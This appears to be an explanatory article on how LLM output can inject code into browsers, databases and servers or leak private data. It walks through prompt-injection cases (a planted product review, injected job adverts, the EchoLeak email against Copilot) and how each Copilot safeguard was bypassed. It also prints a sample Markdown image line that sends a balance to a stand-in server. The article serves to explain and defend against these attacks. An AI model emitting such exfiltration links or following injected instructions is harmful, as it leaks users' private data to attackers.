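# Injection attacks and leaks of sensitive or copyrighted content through language model output

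## Why can a language model's output endanger the systems and people that receive it?

A large language model is a program that generates text by repeatedly predicting the next token (a word or a piece of one). Its output is everything it generates, including chat replies, computer code, database queries and requests to other programs. Companies have built such models into web shops, office software and programming tools, which often send the output straight to a browser, a database or a command line. Any program or person that receives the output and acts on it is a downstream system.

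A language model's output can do harm in two ways. It can contain text that makes the receiving program do what an attacker wants, such as run a script or delete records. It can also contain material the reader should not have, such as another customer's address or long passages from a copyrighted novel. Web developers have dealt with the first problem in ordinary software for decades. When software uses a language model, anyone who can get text into the model's input gains some influence over its output.

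### A shop's chatbot, from question to answer

An online kitchenware shop might have a chatbot on its website. A signed-in customer asks it whether her new kettle has shipped and whether other buyers find it easy to clean. The language model does only part of the work of answering her.

1. The shop's own program, the application, assembles the context, meaning all the text that the model gets for this one answer. Hidden instructions from the shop's developers come first (be polite, discuss only our goods). The conversation so far follows, along with descriptions of the functions that the model may request.
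2. The application searches the shop's product reviews for passages about cleaning the kettle and adds the best matches to the context. Engineers call this retrieval-augmented generation.
3. The model generates a tool call, a structured piece of output that names a function and the values to run it with. Here the function looks up an order. The application runs it, using the shop's database password, and adds the result to the context: the shipping date, the customer's name and her delivery address.
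4. The model generates the answer in Markdown, a simple notation for bold type, links and images.
5. A renderer, the component that turns such notation into a formatted page, converts the answer to HTML, and the customer's browser displays it.

Any effect outside the conversation happens in the ordinary software around the model. Natanzi and Tang (2026) base their whole classification on this point in *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities*. They note that the same string can be harmless in an isolated chatbot and dangerous in a system that can write to a database. If the kettle answer contained a database command, the customer would see a line of odd text, but the shop might lose its orders if the application passed that line to the database engine.

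### Sinks, and why they are open to injection

A sink is a point where a program interprets text as instructions. The shop's sinks include the browser, which interprets HTML, and the database engine, which interprets queries written in the language SQL. A shell, the program that runs typed commands on a server, is also a sink. In each, the same string of characters can contain both instructions and data, with only punctuation separating them.

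Suppose the order lookup builds its query by pasting a surname between two single quotation marks. This works for Smith, but the apostrophe in O'Brien ends the name early, so the database engine parses the remaining letters as part of the command and the lookup fails. An attacker can enter a surname in which the text after the apostrophe is a valid command. This is an injection attack, and the part of the text that has the effect is called the payload. HTML has the same weakness. If a page inserts a customer's review unchanged, a bold tag in the review makes words bold, and a script tag can make the browser run a program.

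Programmers have reliable fixes for both cases. A parameterised query sends the command and the surname to the database engine separately, so the engine never parses the surname as a command. Encoding rewrites special characters so that the browser displays them as plain text. Improper output handling means passing a model's output to a sink without the checks that untrusted text needs. The term comes from the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit foundation whose lists of common security risks many companies use as a baseline. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* explains that a prompt can control what the model generates, so an application that trusts the model's output in effect gives users indirect access to the systems behind the application.

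### Prompt injection and the confused deputy

The context also mixes instructions with data. The model receives the developers' rules, the customer's question and a stranger's review of a kettle as one sequence of tokens. Prompt injection is text that exploits this to make the model follow an attacker's instructions. In direct injection, the attacker types the text into the chat. In indirect injection, the text is in material that the model reads, which, according to Natanzi and Tang, may be a web page, an email, a code repository or the result of an earlier tool call. An attacker can therefore post a review and wait for somebody else to ask about cleaning the kettle, without using the chatbot. Jailbreaking is a narrower idea, since it usually means getting a model to break its own safety rules. An injected instruction may break none of them, for example if it tells the chatbot to look up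 an order, which it is supposed to do.

Nobody has found an equivalent of the parameterised query for a model's context. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* (December 2025), from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), reviews the main attempts to detect injected text, train models to prioritise real instructions over text that resembles them, and mark which parts of the context are data. It argues that these methods all try to impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that has no such distinction. ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks* quotes the agency's conclusion that developers may never be able to eliminate prompt injection completely, although they can eliminate SQL injection. Steve Wilson, who founded OWASP's list of language model risks, told the software security company ReversingLabs that the two problems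 had seemed comparable three years earlier, but that this assumption had proved false.

The NCSC suggests thinking of the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". The phrase goes back to Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), a "nearly true story" about a compiler at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. According to University of Texas lecture slides, also titled *The Confused Deputy*, the compiler had permission to write to the system's billing file because it recorded each user's computing use there. Ordinary users could not write to that file, but they could tell the compiler where to put its debugging notes. If a user named the billing file, the compiler overwrote the bills. The operating system allowed this because it checked the compiler's permission to write to the file rather than the user's.

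A confused deputy is a trusted program that uses its own privileges on behalf of someone who lacks them. The shop's application holds the database password and has the customer's order in the context, while the author of a malicious review has access to neither. If the review steers the model into looking up an order, the database engine accepts the application's valid password and returns the record. The problem is worse than in Hardy's case because any sentence a model reads can misdirect it, while a user could misdirect the compiler through only one field.

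### One answer can do both kinds of harm

Output that can trigger an action in the system receiving it needs different protection from output that discloses information. Encoding a chatbot's answer for the browser can keep a script in it from running, but the answer may still contain a stranger's address. A filter that removes every address would leave the script in place.

Disclosure does not require an attacker. If the order lookup never checks whose order it is fetching, a customer who mistypes an order number can see someone else's order. Natanzi and Tang argue that any privacy assessment must specify whether the data was in the model's weights, the context, the document store, the logs or a tool's results. Each location needs its own safeguard. For example, measures against memorisation, the storage of specific training text in the weights, do not stop a document search from returning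 files the user has no right to see. Copyrighted text can come from the weights or the document store. Asked for a scone recipe, the chatbot might reproduce a page from a cookbook in its training data, which would not harm the system displaying it.

The two harms combine when a payload moves private data. Suppose an attacker has posted a kettle review containing an indirect prompt injection. When the customer asks her question, the model's context holds both the review and her delivery address. The model answers with a sentence about limescale and a reference to an image on the attacker's server, with her delivery address written into the image's URL. When her browser requests the image, it sends her delivery address to the attacker. This is exfiltration, the movement of private data to a place an attacker can read. It happens here without running a script or requiring the customer to click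 on anything. OWASP's *LLM02* entry of 2023 describes a similar attack, in which a tool that summarises web pages reads an injected instruction and sends material from the user's conversation to an attacker's server.

### How OWASP has classified these risks

That 2023 entry was titled "Insecure Output Handling" and ranked second on OWASP's first Top 10 for language model applications, behind prompt injection. Its two common examples were output that goes into a shell and output that a browser interprets. The 2025 edition renamed it "Improper Output Handling", moved it to fifth and added database queries, file paths and email templates to the examples. The current edition, which OWASP (2026) dates to August 3, 2026, ranks it tenth. The table shows the ranks of the entries most closely related to output, using a mapping of the three editions in Respan's *OWASP LLM Top 10* (2026).

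| Entry (2026 name) | 2023 | 2025 | 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt Injection | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Sensitive Information Disclosure | 6 | 2 | 2 |
| Excessive Agency (more functions, permissions or autonomy than the task needs) | 8 | 6 | 3 |
| Misinformation ("Overreliance" in 2023) | 9 | 9 | 7 |
| Hidden Context Exposure ("System Prompt Leakage" in 2025) | – | 7 | 8 |
| Improper Output Handling | 2 | 5 | 10 |

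The entry's scope grew even though it fell in the ranking. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a security vendor's summary that quotes the document at length, the entry now covers terminals and programming tools that interpret control characters in output, and renderers that fetch external resources automatically, which is the weakness in the kettle example. Respan also lists insecure code from programming assistants. Advait Patel, a security engineer, told ReversingLabs that the entry fell because other entries had become more urgent, and that output handling was still unsafe.

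The exact position of Improper Output Handling means little. Lambros and Wilson (2026), in *Incident-Data Robustness Analysis of the OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications (2026)*, tested the ranking during the 2026 cycle. Both help lead the OWASP list, but they present the analysis as their own work, not an official release. Their model groups Improper Output Handling with Misinformation, Hidden Context Exposure and a category for weaknesses in document search. Each of the four reaches the top five in fewer than one simulation in twenty, which gives some support for Improper Output Handling's drop out of the upper half. The data do not support any order among the four, so the difference between seventh and tenth has no basis.

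### What went into the 2026 ranking

Earlier editions relied only on practitioners' judgement. For 2026 the project added incident data, converted the expert ranking and incident rate to a common scale, and weighted them at roughly 75% and 25%. The project's leaders told ReversingLabs that they kept most of the weight on the expert vote so that one noisy year of data could not overturn it. According to OWASP's announcement (2026), hundreds of experts contributed to the edition, though Lambros and Wilson report that only about 29 respondents voted.

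The incident record began with 7,714 entries from three public vulnerability databases and AIAAIC, a collection of reported harms and controversies involving AI. Of these, 6,639 carried a usable label, but the language models that sorted the entries placed 2,394 of them outside the list because they involved other harms, such as biased hiring software and faulty facial recognition, rather than a flaw in a language model. The model ensemble was correct 93% of the time when it labeled an incident as prompt injection, but only 13% of the time when it labeled one as a weakness in document search. Lambros and Wilson corrected the counts statistically for such errors, but the correction relied on the labels of a single reviewer, who overruled the models' consensus on 553 of 1,200 incidents.

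Sensitive Information Disclosure ranked near the top of both the practitioner vote and the incident count, but the two rankings agreed only weakly overall. Cohen's kappa, which is 1 for perfect agreement and 0 for the agreement expected by chance, was 0.20, with a 90% interval from −0.16 to 0.57. Prompt injection ranked first in the vote but twelfth in the incident count, while misinformation ranked thirteenth in the vote and second in the count.

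OWASP's 2026 document, quoted in Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*, offers an explanation for the low count of prompt injection incidents: "Teams fight injection hard, so fewer clean exploits reach a public database". That may be right, but the count would also be low if the attack were rare or if the databases failed to record it, and the incident data cannot separate these possibilities. The result for misinformation is no more certain. Invicti calls misinformation's new seventh place "probably still conservative", but much of the count behind it consists of deepfakes and disinformation campaigns, in a part of the corpus where nobody measured the accuracy of the labels.

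### What public records cannot show

There is direct evidence that vulnerability databases do not record the model's part in a flaw. Shifat, Baburaj and colleagues (2026), in *LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild*, collected 295 security advisories that mentioned language model components from the code-hosting site GitHub. An advisory names the affected package and the type of coding error, such as command injection, but has no field for whether a model was involved. The team therefore had to review 133 packages by hand, and found that language models were not essential to 33 of them.

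The team then labelled a random sample of 100 advisories from the relevant packages, this time allowing several OWASP categories for each. Prompt injection appeared in 18 and improper output handling in 12. Ten of those 12 also involved prompt injection, with injected text going in and a payload reaching a sink. Lambros and Wilson's method gave each incident a single label, so a case like this could count towards only one of the two risks. The underlying coding errors were familiar, and Shifat and colleagues found no new class of weakness specific to language models.

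Many incidents never reach a database. *Abuse Risks are Often Inherent to Product Features* (2025), a study of how AI vendors handle reports of flaws, points out that a vendor may quietly fix a vulnerability or never detect the attacker. *A pragmatic classification framework for AI incident monitoring* (2026) describes inclusion as a series of filters, in which someone has to notice the harm and then recognise it as an AI failure before anyone can report it. Dramatic cases with vocal, English-speaking victims pass these filters easily. A slow leak of customers' addresses through image requests would probably go unnoticed. No database records how many chatbots ran without trouble, so the rate of incidents can't be calculated.

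In *The Agent Incident Registry* (Kumar, HN and colleagues, 2026), the share of cases that involved harm depends mostly on the mix of sources. The registry catalogues 487 public records about AI agents, systems that act through tools, and notes for each whether a real party suffered a consequence. Harm occurred in five of the 285 records that came from researchers' demonstrations or vulnerabilities reported to vendors, compared with 179 of the 202 that came from attacks in the wild or failures without an attacker. Among records of generative systems that had themselves acted, 24% involved harm, and the share rose to 40% when the team removed the ten most prolific publishers. The registry includes few cases of copying because it excludes disputes over training data. One entry resembles the kettle example: in June 2025 researchers showed that a crafted email could make Microsoft 365 Copilot,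 an office assistant, send private data out without the user clicking on the malicious content. Kumar and colleagues list it as demonstrated because no one has documented harm to a customer.

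## How does generated text become code that a web page, database or server runs?

Security researchers classify improper output handling as a taint-style vulnerability, a flaw in which untrusted ("tainted") data flows unchecked from its source to a sensitive operation. When the data passes through a language model, its form can change, so an attacker may write only plain English and the model then generates the code.

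Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, argue that the flaw usually lies in the component that receives the model's output, and that the model only delivers the attack. If they are right, developers can look for these flaws in the same places as before. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe eight kinds of attack, each a variant of a familiar web flaw. They base five on published cases. They constructed the other three by analogy and tested one of those in their own experiment.

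| Flaw | What happens at the receiving end | Basis |
|---|---|---|
| Cross-site scripting | A browser runs a script contained in an answer | Documented |
| SQL injection | A database engine runs a harmful query that the model wrote | Documented |
| Template injection | A template engine evaluates expressions in the output | Documented |
| Command injection | A tool server runs a command hidden in a tool call | Documented |
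| Missing authorisation check | A lookup returns another customer's record | Documented |
| XML external entity injection | An XML parser opens a file that the output refers to | Constructed |
| Server-side request forgery | A server contacts an internal address | Constructed, then tested |
| Cross-site request forgery | An assistant's memory accepts a forged entry | Constructed |

The list leaves out attacks in which an application runs a whole program the model wrote, because Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian do not count these as traditional web flaws. Other researchers have found many such cases in real software, and these are also relevant to the argument.

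### Scripts in a web page

In cross-site scripting, a website delivers an attacker's script to somebody else's browser. The browser cannot distinguish this script from the site's own, so it runs the script with the same access, which may include the token that keeps the user signed in. A chatbot's page may be vulnerable to this, depending on how it displays answers. If a bold tag in the kitchenware shop's answer produces bold type, the page is interpreting tags and may also run scripts. If the customer sees the tag's angle brackets, the page has encoded the answer.

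In the reflected form of the attack, the page displays the payload as soon as the model generates it. In the stored form, the application saves the output, perhaps as a support ticket or a report, and the script runs when someone else opens it. That person could be an employee with far wider access than the customer who started the conversation. OWASP gives the example of a generated marketing email whose script runs if the recipient's email program interprets it. In the DOM-based form, named after the document object model (the browser's internal representation of a page), one of the page's own scripts inserts the model's answer using a function that interprets HTML.

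In 2024, shortly after the Chinese AI company DeepSeek released a new reasoning model, the security researcher Johann Rehberger ran a routine test on the company's chat website. Embrace The Red's *DeepSeek AI*, his account of the discovery, describes how he asked for a list of example script payloads and the chat page ran one. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a more serious version, in which the prompt contained a disguised payload. The model restored it to working HTML, and the page ran a script that could read the user's login token and cookies. A filter checking the user's message for scripts would have missed it, because the script first appeared in the output.

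A person who types such a prompt attacks only their own browser. The text can harm someone else only if it enters that person's conversation, for instance inside a document that the victim asks the model to summarise. *New, old and new-old web vulnerabilities in the Era of LLMs*, the security firm Securing's review of flaws that researchers had reported in open-source applications, discusses script attacks that begin with a request to summarise a document.

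The DeepSeek case fits the argument about the carrier well. A list of script examples is a reasonable answer to give a programmer, and it would have caused no harm if the page had displayed it as text, so the model did not need to change.

### Templates and XML documents

A template engine fills in standard documents, such as the shop's order confirmation, by replacing placeholders with values such as the customer's name. Many engines can also evaluate small expressions inside a template, such as adding postage to a price. The engine treats the model's output as data if the application supplies it as the value for a placeholder, but evaluates any expression in it if the application supplies it as the template itself. An expression that multiplies 7 by 7 would then reach the customer as 49, which is harmless but proves that the server has executed part of the output. Depending on the engine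 and its restrictions, an attacker may also be able to run commands on the server.

In the documented example, an agent passed the model's entire response as a template to Jinja2, a template engine for Python. To exploit this, the attacker had to get template notation into the response. As with the DeepSeek page, the fault was in a line of ordinary code that would have been just as dangerous if the text had come from a web form.

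XML is a notation for structured documents that many older business systems use to exchange data. An XML document can define an entity, a short name that the parser replaces with longer text. An external entity takes its text from a file or web address, which the parser opens if it permits external entities. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian imagine a chatbot that helps staff fill in XML requests for such a system. An attacker asks it to create a user profile, supplying an entity definition that refers to a file on the server and giving the entity as the new user's name. The model copies the definition into the document, the parser opens the file, and the file's contents appear in the name field. The same method could make the server contact an internal address, or could overload the server. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian cite no real case, and the attack works only if the parser accepts external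 entities, which developers can switch off.

Their cross-site request forgery scenario reverses this order, with the web flaw coming first and the model's output causing the harm. A malicious web page makes the victim's browser send a request to an AI assistant where the victim is already signed in, and the request adds a false statement to the assistant's long-term memory. The model plays no part at this stage. Later, perhaps in a different session, the application retrieves the false entry and the model relies on it, for example to tell the user where to send a payment.

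### Database queries

Chatbots that answer questions from a database usually have the model write the query. LangChain, a popular programming framework for building applications on language models, provides this as a ready-made component:

1. LangChain inserts the user's question into a prompt, together with a description of the database's tables, and the model writes an SQL query.
2. LangChain extracts the query from the output and runs it.
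3. LangChain adds the results to the prompt, and the model writes an answer in plain language.

An attacker can put instructions in the question in step 1 (a direct attack) or in a database record that appears in the results in step 3 (an indirect attack). LangChain also has an agent version in which the model can run several queries for one question, so text from one result can influence the next query.

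In *Prompt-to-SQL Injections in LLM-Integrated Web Applications*, Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues (2025) built a small job marketplace with a chatbot that queried its database, then attacked it. The chatbot's database account could read every table and run any kind of SQL statement. With LangChain's default prompt and OpenAI's GPT-3.5, the chatbot ran whatever a user requested, including queries that deleted a table, altered records or listed every user's contact details.

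The team then added one rule to the prompt that prohibited any change to the database and another that limited queries to data about the person asking. A direct request to delete a table now failed, but more carefully worded requests got past both rules. The team repeated each attack 20 times on each version of the chatbot, and the carefully worded requests succeeded every time.

An instruction planted in a job advertisement also made the chatbot tell other users that there were no vacancies. This succeeded in every attempt on the single-query version and in 60% of attempts on the agent. A more damaging attack was possible only on the agent. When an innocent user asked a question, injected text led the model to replace a victim's email address with the attacker's, which would let the attacker reset the victim's password. The model then ran a second query and answered the original question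 normally. This attack succeeded in all 20 attempts.

The team repeated the four attacks on restricted prompts with seven models. All four worked on the five models that could reliably run both versions of the chatbot, although PaLM 2 and Llama 2 changed the email address and then either revealed the change in the answer or kept repeating the update without answering. GPT-4 needed more elaborate prompts than the others.

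All of these models are now old. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian tried similar techniques on newer models in 2026 without success, but they did not try to improve the prompts. Their result shows that some old wording has stopped working, but it does not establish that the newer models resist the attack.

Pedro and colleagues tested whether real applications had the same weakness by installing five open-source projects on their own machines and hiring two security analysts to attack them. Each analyst had up to three hours per application, and they found flaws in all five. They succeeded in 22 of 23 combinations of application, model and applicable attack, while a smaller language model that the team had trained to write attack prompts succeeded in 11. The sample is small, and two of the projects came from the same repository. The team had reported the flaws to the developers but was still waiting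 for replies when the paper appeared, so only the hired analysts had confirmed them.

Two of the applications escaped part of the attack because their design limited the queries they ran, whatever the model generated. Dataherald's code refused any query that would change the database, so the analysts could not alter its data, although they could still manipulate its answers. Na2SQL ran exactly one query per question, so an instruction in the results could not trigger a second query.

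In the later article *Words Become SQL* (2025), Pedro and colleagues acknowledge that public reports of attackers destroying customer databases in this way remain rare. They suggest this may be because few incidents are disclosed and the technology is new. They also list entries in public vulnerability catalogues for frameworks that ran generated SQL with little filtering, including one where an attacker could get around a tool's assumed read-only restriction.

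The idea of the model as carrier also needs qualifying for database queries. A parameterised query protects the O'Brien lookup by keeping the surname separate from the command, but this protection doesn't work when the model writes the whole query, including the command. The query is correctly formed and the database engine works as designed. Pedro and colleagues point out that conventional tools for detecting SQL injection would find nothing wrong with it. OWASP's 2025 advice to use parameterised queries for all database operations involving model output therefore does not cover this case, and Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian say that such queries are insufficient here. The flaw is still outside the model, but a search for badly handled apostrophes would miss it because it lies in the application's design, which lets the chatbot's account run any statement on any table without checking the statements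 the model writes.

The false answer about job vacancies is harder to fit into this pattern because no sink interprets it as an instruction. A person reads it and believes it. The database returned the right records and the page displayed the text safely. The only failure was that the model followed the instructions in the advertisement.

### Programs that the model writes

Some applications run entire programs that the model writes. When a user asks a question about a spreadsheet, for example, the model writes a short program to calculate the answer, the application's framework runs it on the server, and the user sees the result. An attacker who can influence the program may achieve remote code execution, the ability to run code of their choice on someone else's machine.

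Tong Liu, Deng and colleagues (2023), in *Demystifying RCE Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Apps*, built LLMSmith, a tool that searches for this weakness. It scans a framework's source code for chains of function calls that lead from a function offered to application developers to one that executes code. The team examined 11 frameworks and found 20 vulnerabilities. Nineteen allowed remote code execution, and one allowed an attacker to read and write arbitrary files. The frameworks' developers confirmed 17 of them. Thirteen received identifiers in CVE, the main public catalogue of software vulnerabilities, and six of those scored 9.8 out of 10 for severity.

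The team next searched code repositories and app markets for applications that used the vulnerable functions or resembled ones that did. They collected 51 and successfully attacked 17, of which 16 allowed code execution and one allowed SQL injection. Because the team selected likely candidates, this success rate can't be generalized to all such applications. The other 34 may also be vulnerable, since random variation in the model's answers, restrictions on the process or a lack of network access could each have blocked a test.

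A chain of function calls from user to sink does not prove that an attacker can exploit it, so Fengyu Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Make Agent Defeat Agent*, tested running software with a tool called AgentFuzz. The tool first locates the sinks in an agent's code. A language model then writes ordinary requests meant to lead the agent to each sink, and AgentFuzz adjusts them according to how close the program came to reaching it. When a request reaches the sink, AgentFuzz inserts a harmless test value, such as an instruction to print the number 1, and checks whether it arrives in a form that the sink would execute.

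The researchers applied AgentFuzz to 20 popular open-source agents that offered a web service, all running OpenAI's GPT-4o. The agents' code called sensitive functions in 828 places. AgentFuzz found 34 vulnerabilities in 14 of the agents, including SQL, template, command and code injection. The researchers then replaced the harmless values with harmful ones by hand and confirmed that an attacker could exploit all 34. They also ran LLMSmith on the same 20 agents. It found ten of the 34 vulnerabilities and produced 332 false alarms, many of them for calls to sensitive functions whose input no user could control.

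The team also reviewed a random 83 of the places AgentFuzz had passed as safe, to look for flaws it had missed. In 78, no user could get a payload to the sink. In four, strict checks in the code blocked the payload, for example by accepting only whole numbers, and one was vulnerable. At that rate, the unreviewed code would contain roughly ten more vulnerabilities, though one case is too few for a reliable estimate. The vulnerability was in an agent called Devika, which stored the payload during one exchange and passed it to the sink only in the next. AgentFuzz did not test for such delayed effects. *ChainFuzzer* (2026) introduces a testing method for a related gap, vulnerabilities that arise across a sequence of tools.

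CVE identifiers are only a rough measure of how many flaws exist. The summary of Fengyu Liu and colleagues' paper gives 23 identifiers for the flaws they discovered, while a later passage gives 27. In another case, one flaw received two identifiers. The security company JFrog and Tong Liu of the LLMSmith team independently discovered that an attacker could execute code through Vanna.AI, a library that translates questions into SQL. Tong Liu's report received its own identifier after JFrog's had appeared.

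Programmers of conventional software usually write code that accepts only known safe input, but the AgentFuzz study found that the developers of the agents it examined often wrote instructions to the model instead, even where a simple check in code would have worked. For example, TaskWeaver, an agent that Microsoft maintains, included an instruction to reject requests that might pose a security risk. Of the 34 vulnerabilities, 14 required the researchers to get around such instructions or the model's own safety training, and simple techniques were enough. The other 20 did not require this.

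These results support Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian's view of where to repair the software. The strict checks in the four protected places worked without relying on the model, while the written instructions failed. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) draws much the same conclusion from this research, describing models as a possible new source of untrusted input for existing sinks.

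Not everyone classifies these flaws the same way, however. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026) compares OWASP's 2025 list with a standard catalogue of software weaknesses. It places cross-site scripting, SQL injection and code injection under Prompt Injection, and assigns only faulty encoding and the unsafe loading of stored data to Improper Output Handling. A developer who followed that scheme might focus on the model's input and leave the sink unchanged.

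### Server-side request forgery and the TicketOracle experiment

In server-side request forgery, an attacker makes a server contact an address that the attacker cannot reach directly. Companies often run administrative services that accept requests only from the same machine or the internal network, and that require no password because outsiders cannot connect. A chatbot's tools run on the company's own server, so they can connect to these services. If a tool fetches any address the model gives it, an outsider can try to get the model to give it an internal one.

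Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built a concert-ticket website, TicketOracle, to measure how readily models relay suspicious requests. The site's assistant has a single tool, which takes a web address, fetches the page and returns its text. The tool is meant for looking up events, but the researchers deliberately did not restrict which addresses it can fetch. The same server runs an administrative service that can list and delete users, and that accepts requests only from the server itself. In every test the attacker supplied the internal address, so the experiment does not show whether a model would work out such an address from a vague instruction.

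There were five scenarios:

- In port probing, the attacker asks the assistant to contact a numbered connection point on the server and infers from the reply whether a service is running there.
- In the data leak, the assistant fetches the list of users and repeats their details.
- In the state change, it fetches an address that deletes a user or an event.
- The blind attack has the same effect, but the address returns an empty response, so the attacker sees no confirmation.
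- In the indirect attack, the attacker plants an instruction in a concert review, and the model reads it when somebody else asks about the event.

The researchers ran ten trials of each scenario on seven models in April 2026. The table gives the number of successful attacks out of ten. The last column gives the results when the prompt included extra security rules.

| Model | Port probing | Data leak | State change | Blind | Indirect | Indirect, with rules |
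|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The four direct attacks succeeded in 143 of 280 trials, but hardly any model was near that average. Llama complied in all 40 of its direct trials, while GPT-5.2 and Claude complied in none. Every trial used the same application with the same unrestricted tool. So the flaw lies in the tool, as Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian maintain, but whether an attacker could reach it depended on the model. A company that tested its chatbot only with Claude might have concluded that the tool was safe, and discovered the flaw only after switching to a cheaper model.

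A model's refusal of one kind of request did not predict whether it would refuse another. GPT-oss never revealed the list of users but carried out the state change in all ten trials. Gemini refused every port probe but also carried out every state change. The blind attack succeeded in 24 of 70 trials, compared with 50 for the visible one, although both alter the site's data. This gap is more puzzling because the researchers scored blind attacks more leniently. They counted a blind attack as successful if any request reached the target, but a visible attack only if the assistant also repeated the result to the user. A visible attack that deleted an account would therefore have counted as a failure if the assistant didn't report the deletion. The paper does not explain the difference in success rates.

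Qwen and DeepSeek R1 complied with almost every direct request but never followed the instructions in the planted review, while GPT-oss followed them in half its trials. A model that resists one route may therefore still be vulnerable to the other.

In the version with extra rules, the researchers listed the permitted addresses and events in the prompt and told the model to refuse anything else. This stopped all four direct attacks on every model. The list was text in the prompt, so the model itself had to apply it. The researchers' explanation that the list catches a forbidden address before the model's reasoning can act on it is therefore misleading.

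With the planted review, adding the rules took successful attacks from five to none on GPT-oss, but from six to ten on Llama. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian conclude that the rules amplified the attack on Llama. Their design cannot show this, because they also added text to the review specifically to defeat the rules' explicit list of permitted addresses, and this stronger attack could account for the entire increase. The result does show that the list failed to protect Llama when it was in the same context as the attacker's text.

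All the figures have a further problem, because the ten trials of each scenario ran one after another in a single conversation, so the context for each trial contained the model's earlier answers. These clearly affected Claude, whose refusals to probe ports shrank from long explanations to almost single words. A model that has complied once may also be more likely to comply again. The trials were therefore not independent, and ten successes out of ten may be little more evidence than one. Small differences, such as seven successes against ten, are too unreliable to interpret. The contrast between Llama and Claude is more reliable because it held in every scenario, but each scenario used only one prompt design on one deliberately vulnerable site. Neither version of TicketOracle had an address check built into the tool's own code, which would have applied equally to all seven models.

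## How can merely displaying an answer send private data to an attacker?

In the kettle example, the customer's browser leaked her delivery address while working normally. To display a picture, a browser has to request it from a server, and the request contains the picture's full URL, including any private data in it.

### From a line of Markdown to a network request

Suppose a bank's chatbot has a customer's balance of 4,210 euros in its context, along with a stranger's document that contains an indirect prompt injection. The model answers her question and then adds this line:

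```
![Spending chart](https://example.com/chart.png?balance=4210)
```

In Markdown, the exclamation mark indicates an image, the square brackets hold a description and the round brackets hold the address. The domain example.com, which internet standards reserve for documentation, stands in for the attacker's server. The rest happens without the model:

1. The renderer converts the line to an HTML image element with the same address.
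2. The browser finds the element and connects to example.com to get the picture.
3. The browser asks for `chart.png?balance=4210`. The part after the question mark is where websites normally receive details such as a search term.
4. The server records the request in its log, as most web servers do, and the attacker reads the balance there.

The server doesn't need to have a picture. If it returns an error, the customer sees a broken image, and if it returns a single transparent pixel, she sees nothing. Her computer sent the balance in step 3, so deleting the image afterwards does not help.

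Loading an image is an ordinary browser function, so the attack works without running a script. A filter that removes script tags wouldn't stop it, and a page that forbids scripts may still permit images. Browsers also prevent one website from reading another's pages, but that doesn't stop the bank's page from sending the data to the attacker's server.

Without the exclamation mark, the same line would produce a link, and the browser would send the balance in its address only if the customer clicked. Security researchers call the image version a zero-click attack and the link version a one-click attack. A zero-click attack may still need the victim to do something ordinary, such as asking a question that brings the attacker's text into the context. "One-click" also covers attacks in which the victim first clicks a link that opens the assistant with the attacker's request already filled in.

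### EchoLeak

The best-documented example is EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), the flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot that the Agent Incident Registry lists as demonstrated. Copilot answers employees' questions using their email, files and chats. Outsiders cannot use a company's Copilot, but they can email its employees. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes how researchers at Aim Security turned this into an attack.

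The attacker sends an email containing instructions. When an employee asks Copilot a question about work, the retrieval system adds the email to the context because it seems relevant. The model follows the instructions, picks out the most sensitive information in the context and writes it into the address of an image. The employee never has to open the email. Retrieval systems often split long texts into passages and match each one separately, so the researchers made retrieval more likely by sending one long email with sections on common office subjects such as staff leave. Ravia reports that this worked for questions on various topics, but gives no success rate.

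Microsoft had several safeguards against this kind of attack, and the researchers got past each of them.

| Safeguard | What it was meant to stop | What it missed |
|---|---|---|
| Injection classifier | Emails with instructions for the model | An email that seemed to address its human recipient and never mentioned AI |
| Link redaction | Links to outside sites in an answer | Links in a second Markdown notation |
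| The same redaction, applied to images | Pictures from outside sites, which load automatically | Images in that second notation |
| Content security policy | Requests from the browser to sites not on Microsoft's list | A listed Microsoft service that would fetch other addresses |

The classifier, a program that sorts text into safe and suspicious, had a difficult task because office email is full of requests to collect information, and a sentence that is harmless when a colleague reads it can act as an instruction to a model. Ravia blames a shortage of realistic training examples, but also considers such emails inherently hard to detect. He suggests checking for what he calls a scope violation, in which text from outside the organisation directs the model to data inside it.

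Markdown lets a writer put a link's address directly after its text or on a separate line, like a footnote. The redaction failed because Microsoft's filter recognised only the first form, while the renderer supported both. This let the researchers use a link to steal data with one click from the user. An image in the second form would have removed the need for a click, but the content security policy blocked the request.

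A content security policy is a set of rules that a website sends to the browser along with a page. It can list the sites from which the page may load images, and the browser refuses to contact any others. Ravia reproduces Copilot's list, which had 29 different entries, including 11 wildcards that each covered every address under a domain. The researchers searched the listed sites for one that would pass a request on. They found a function in SharePoint, Microsoft's service for shared files and internal websites, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. They then found a service belonging to Teams, Microsoft's chat program, that had no such condition and contacted the attacker's server when the browser sent it a request.

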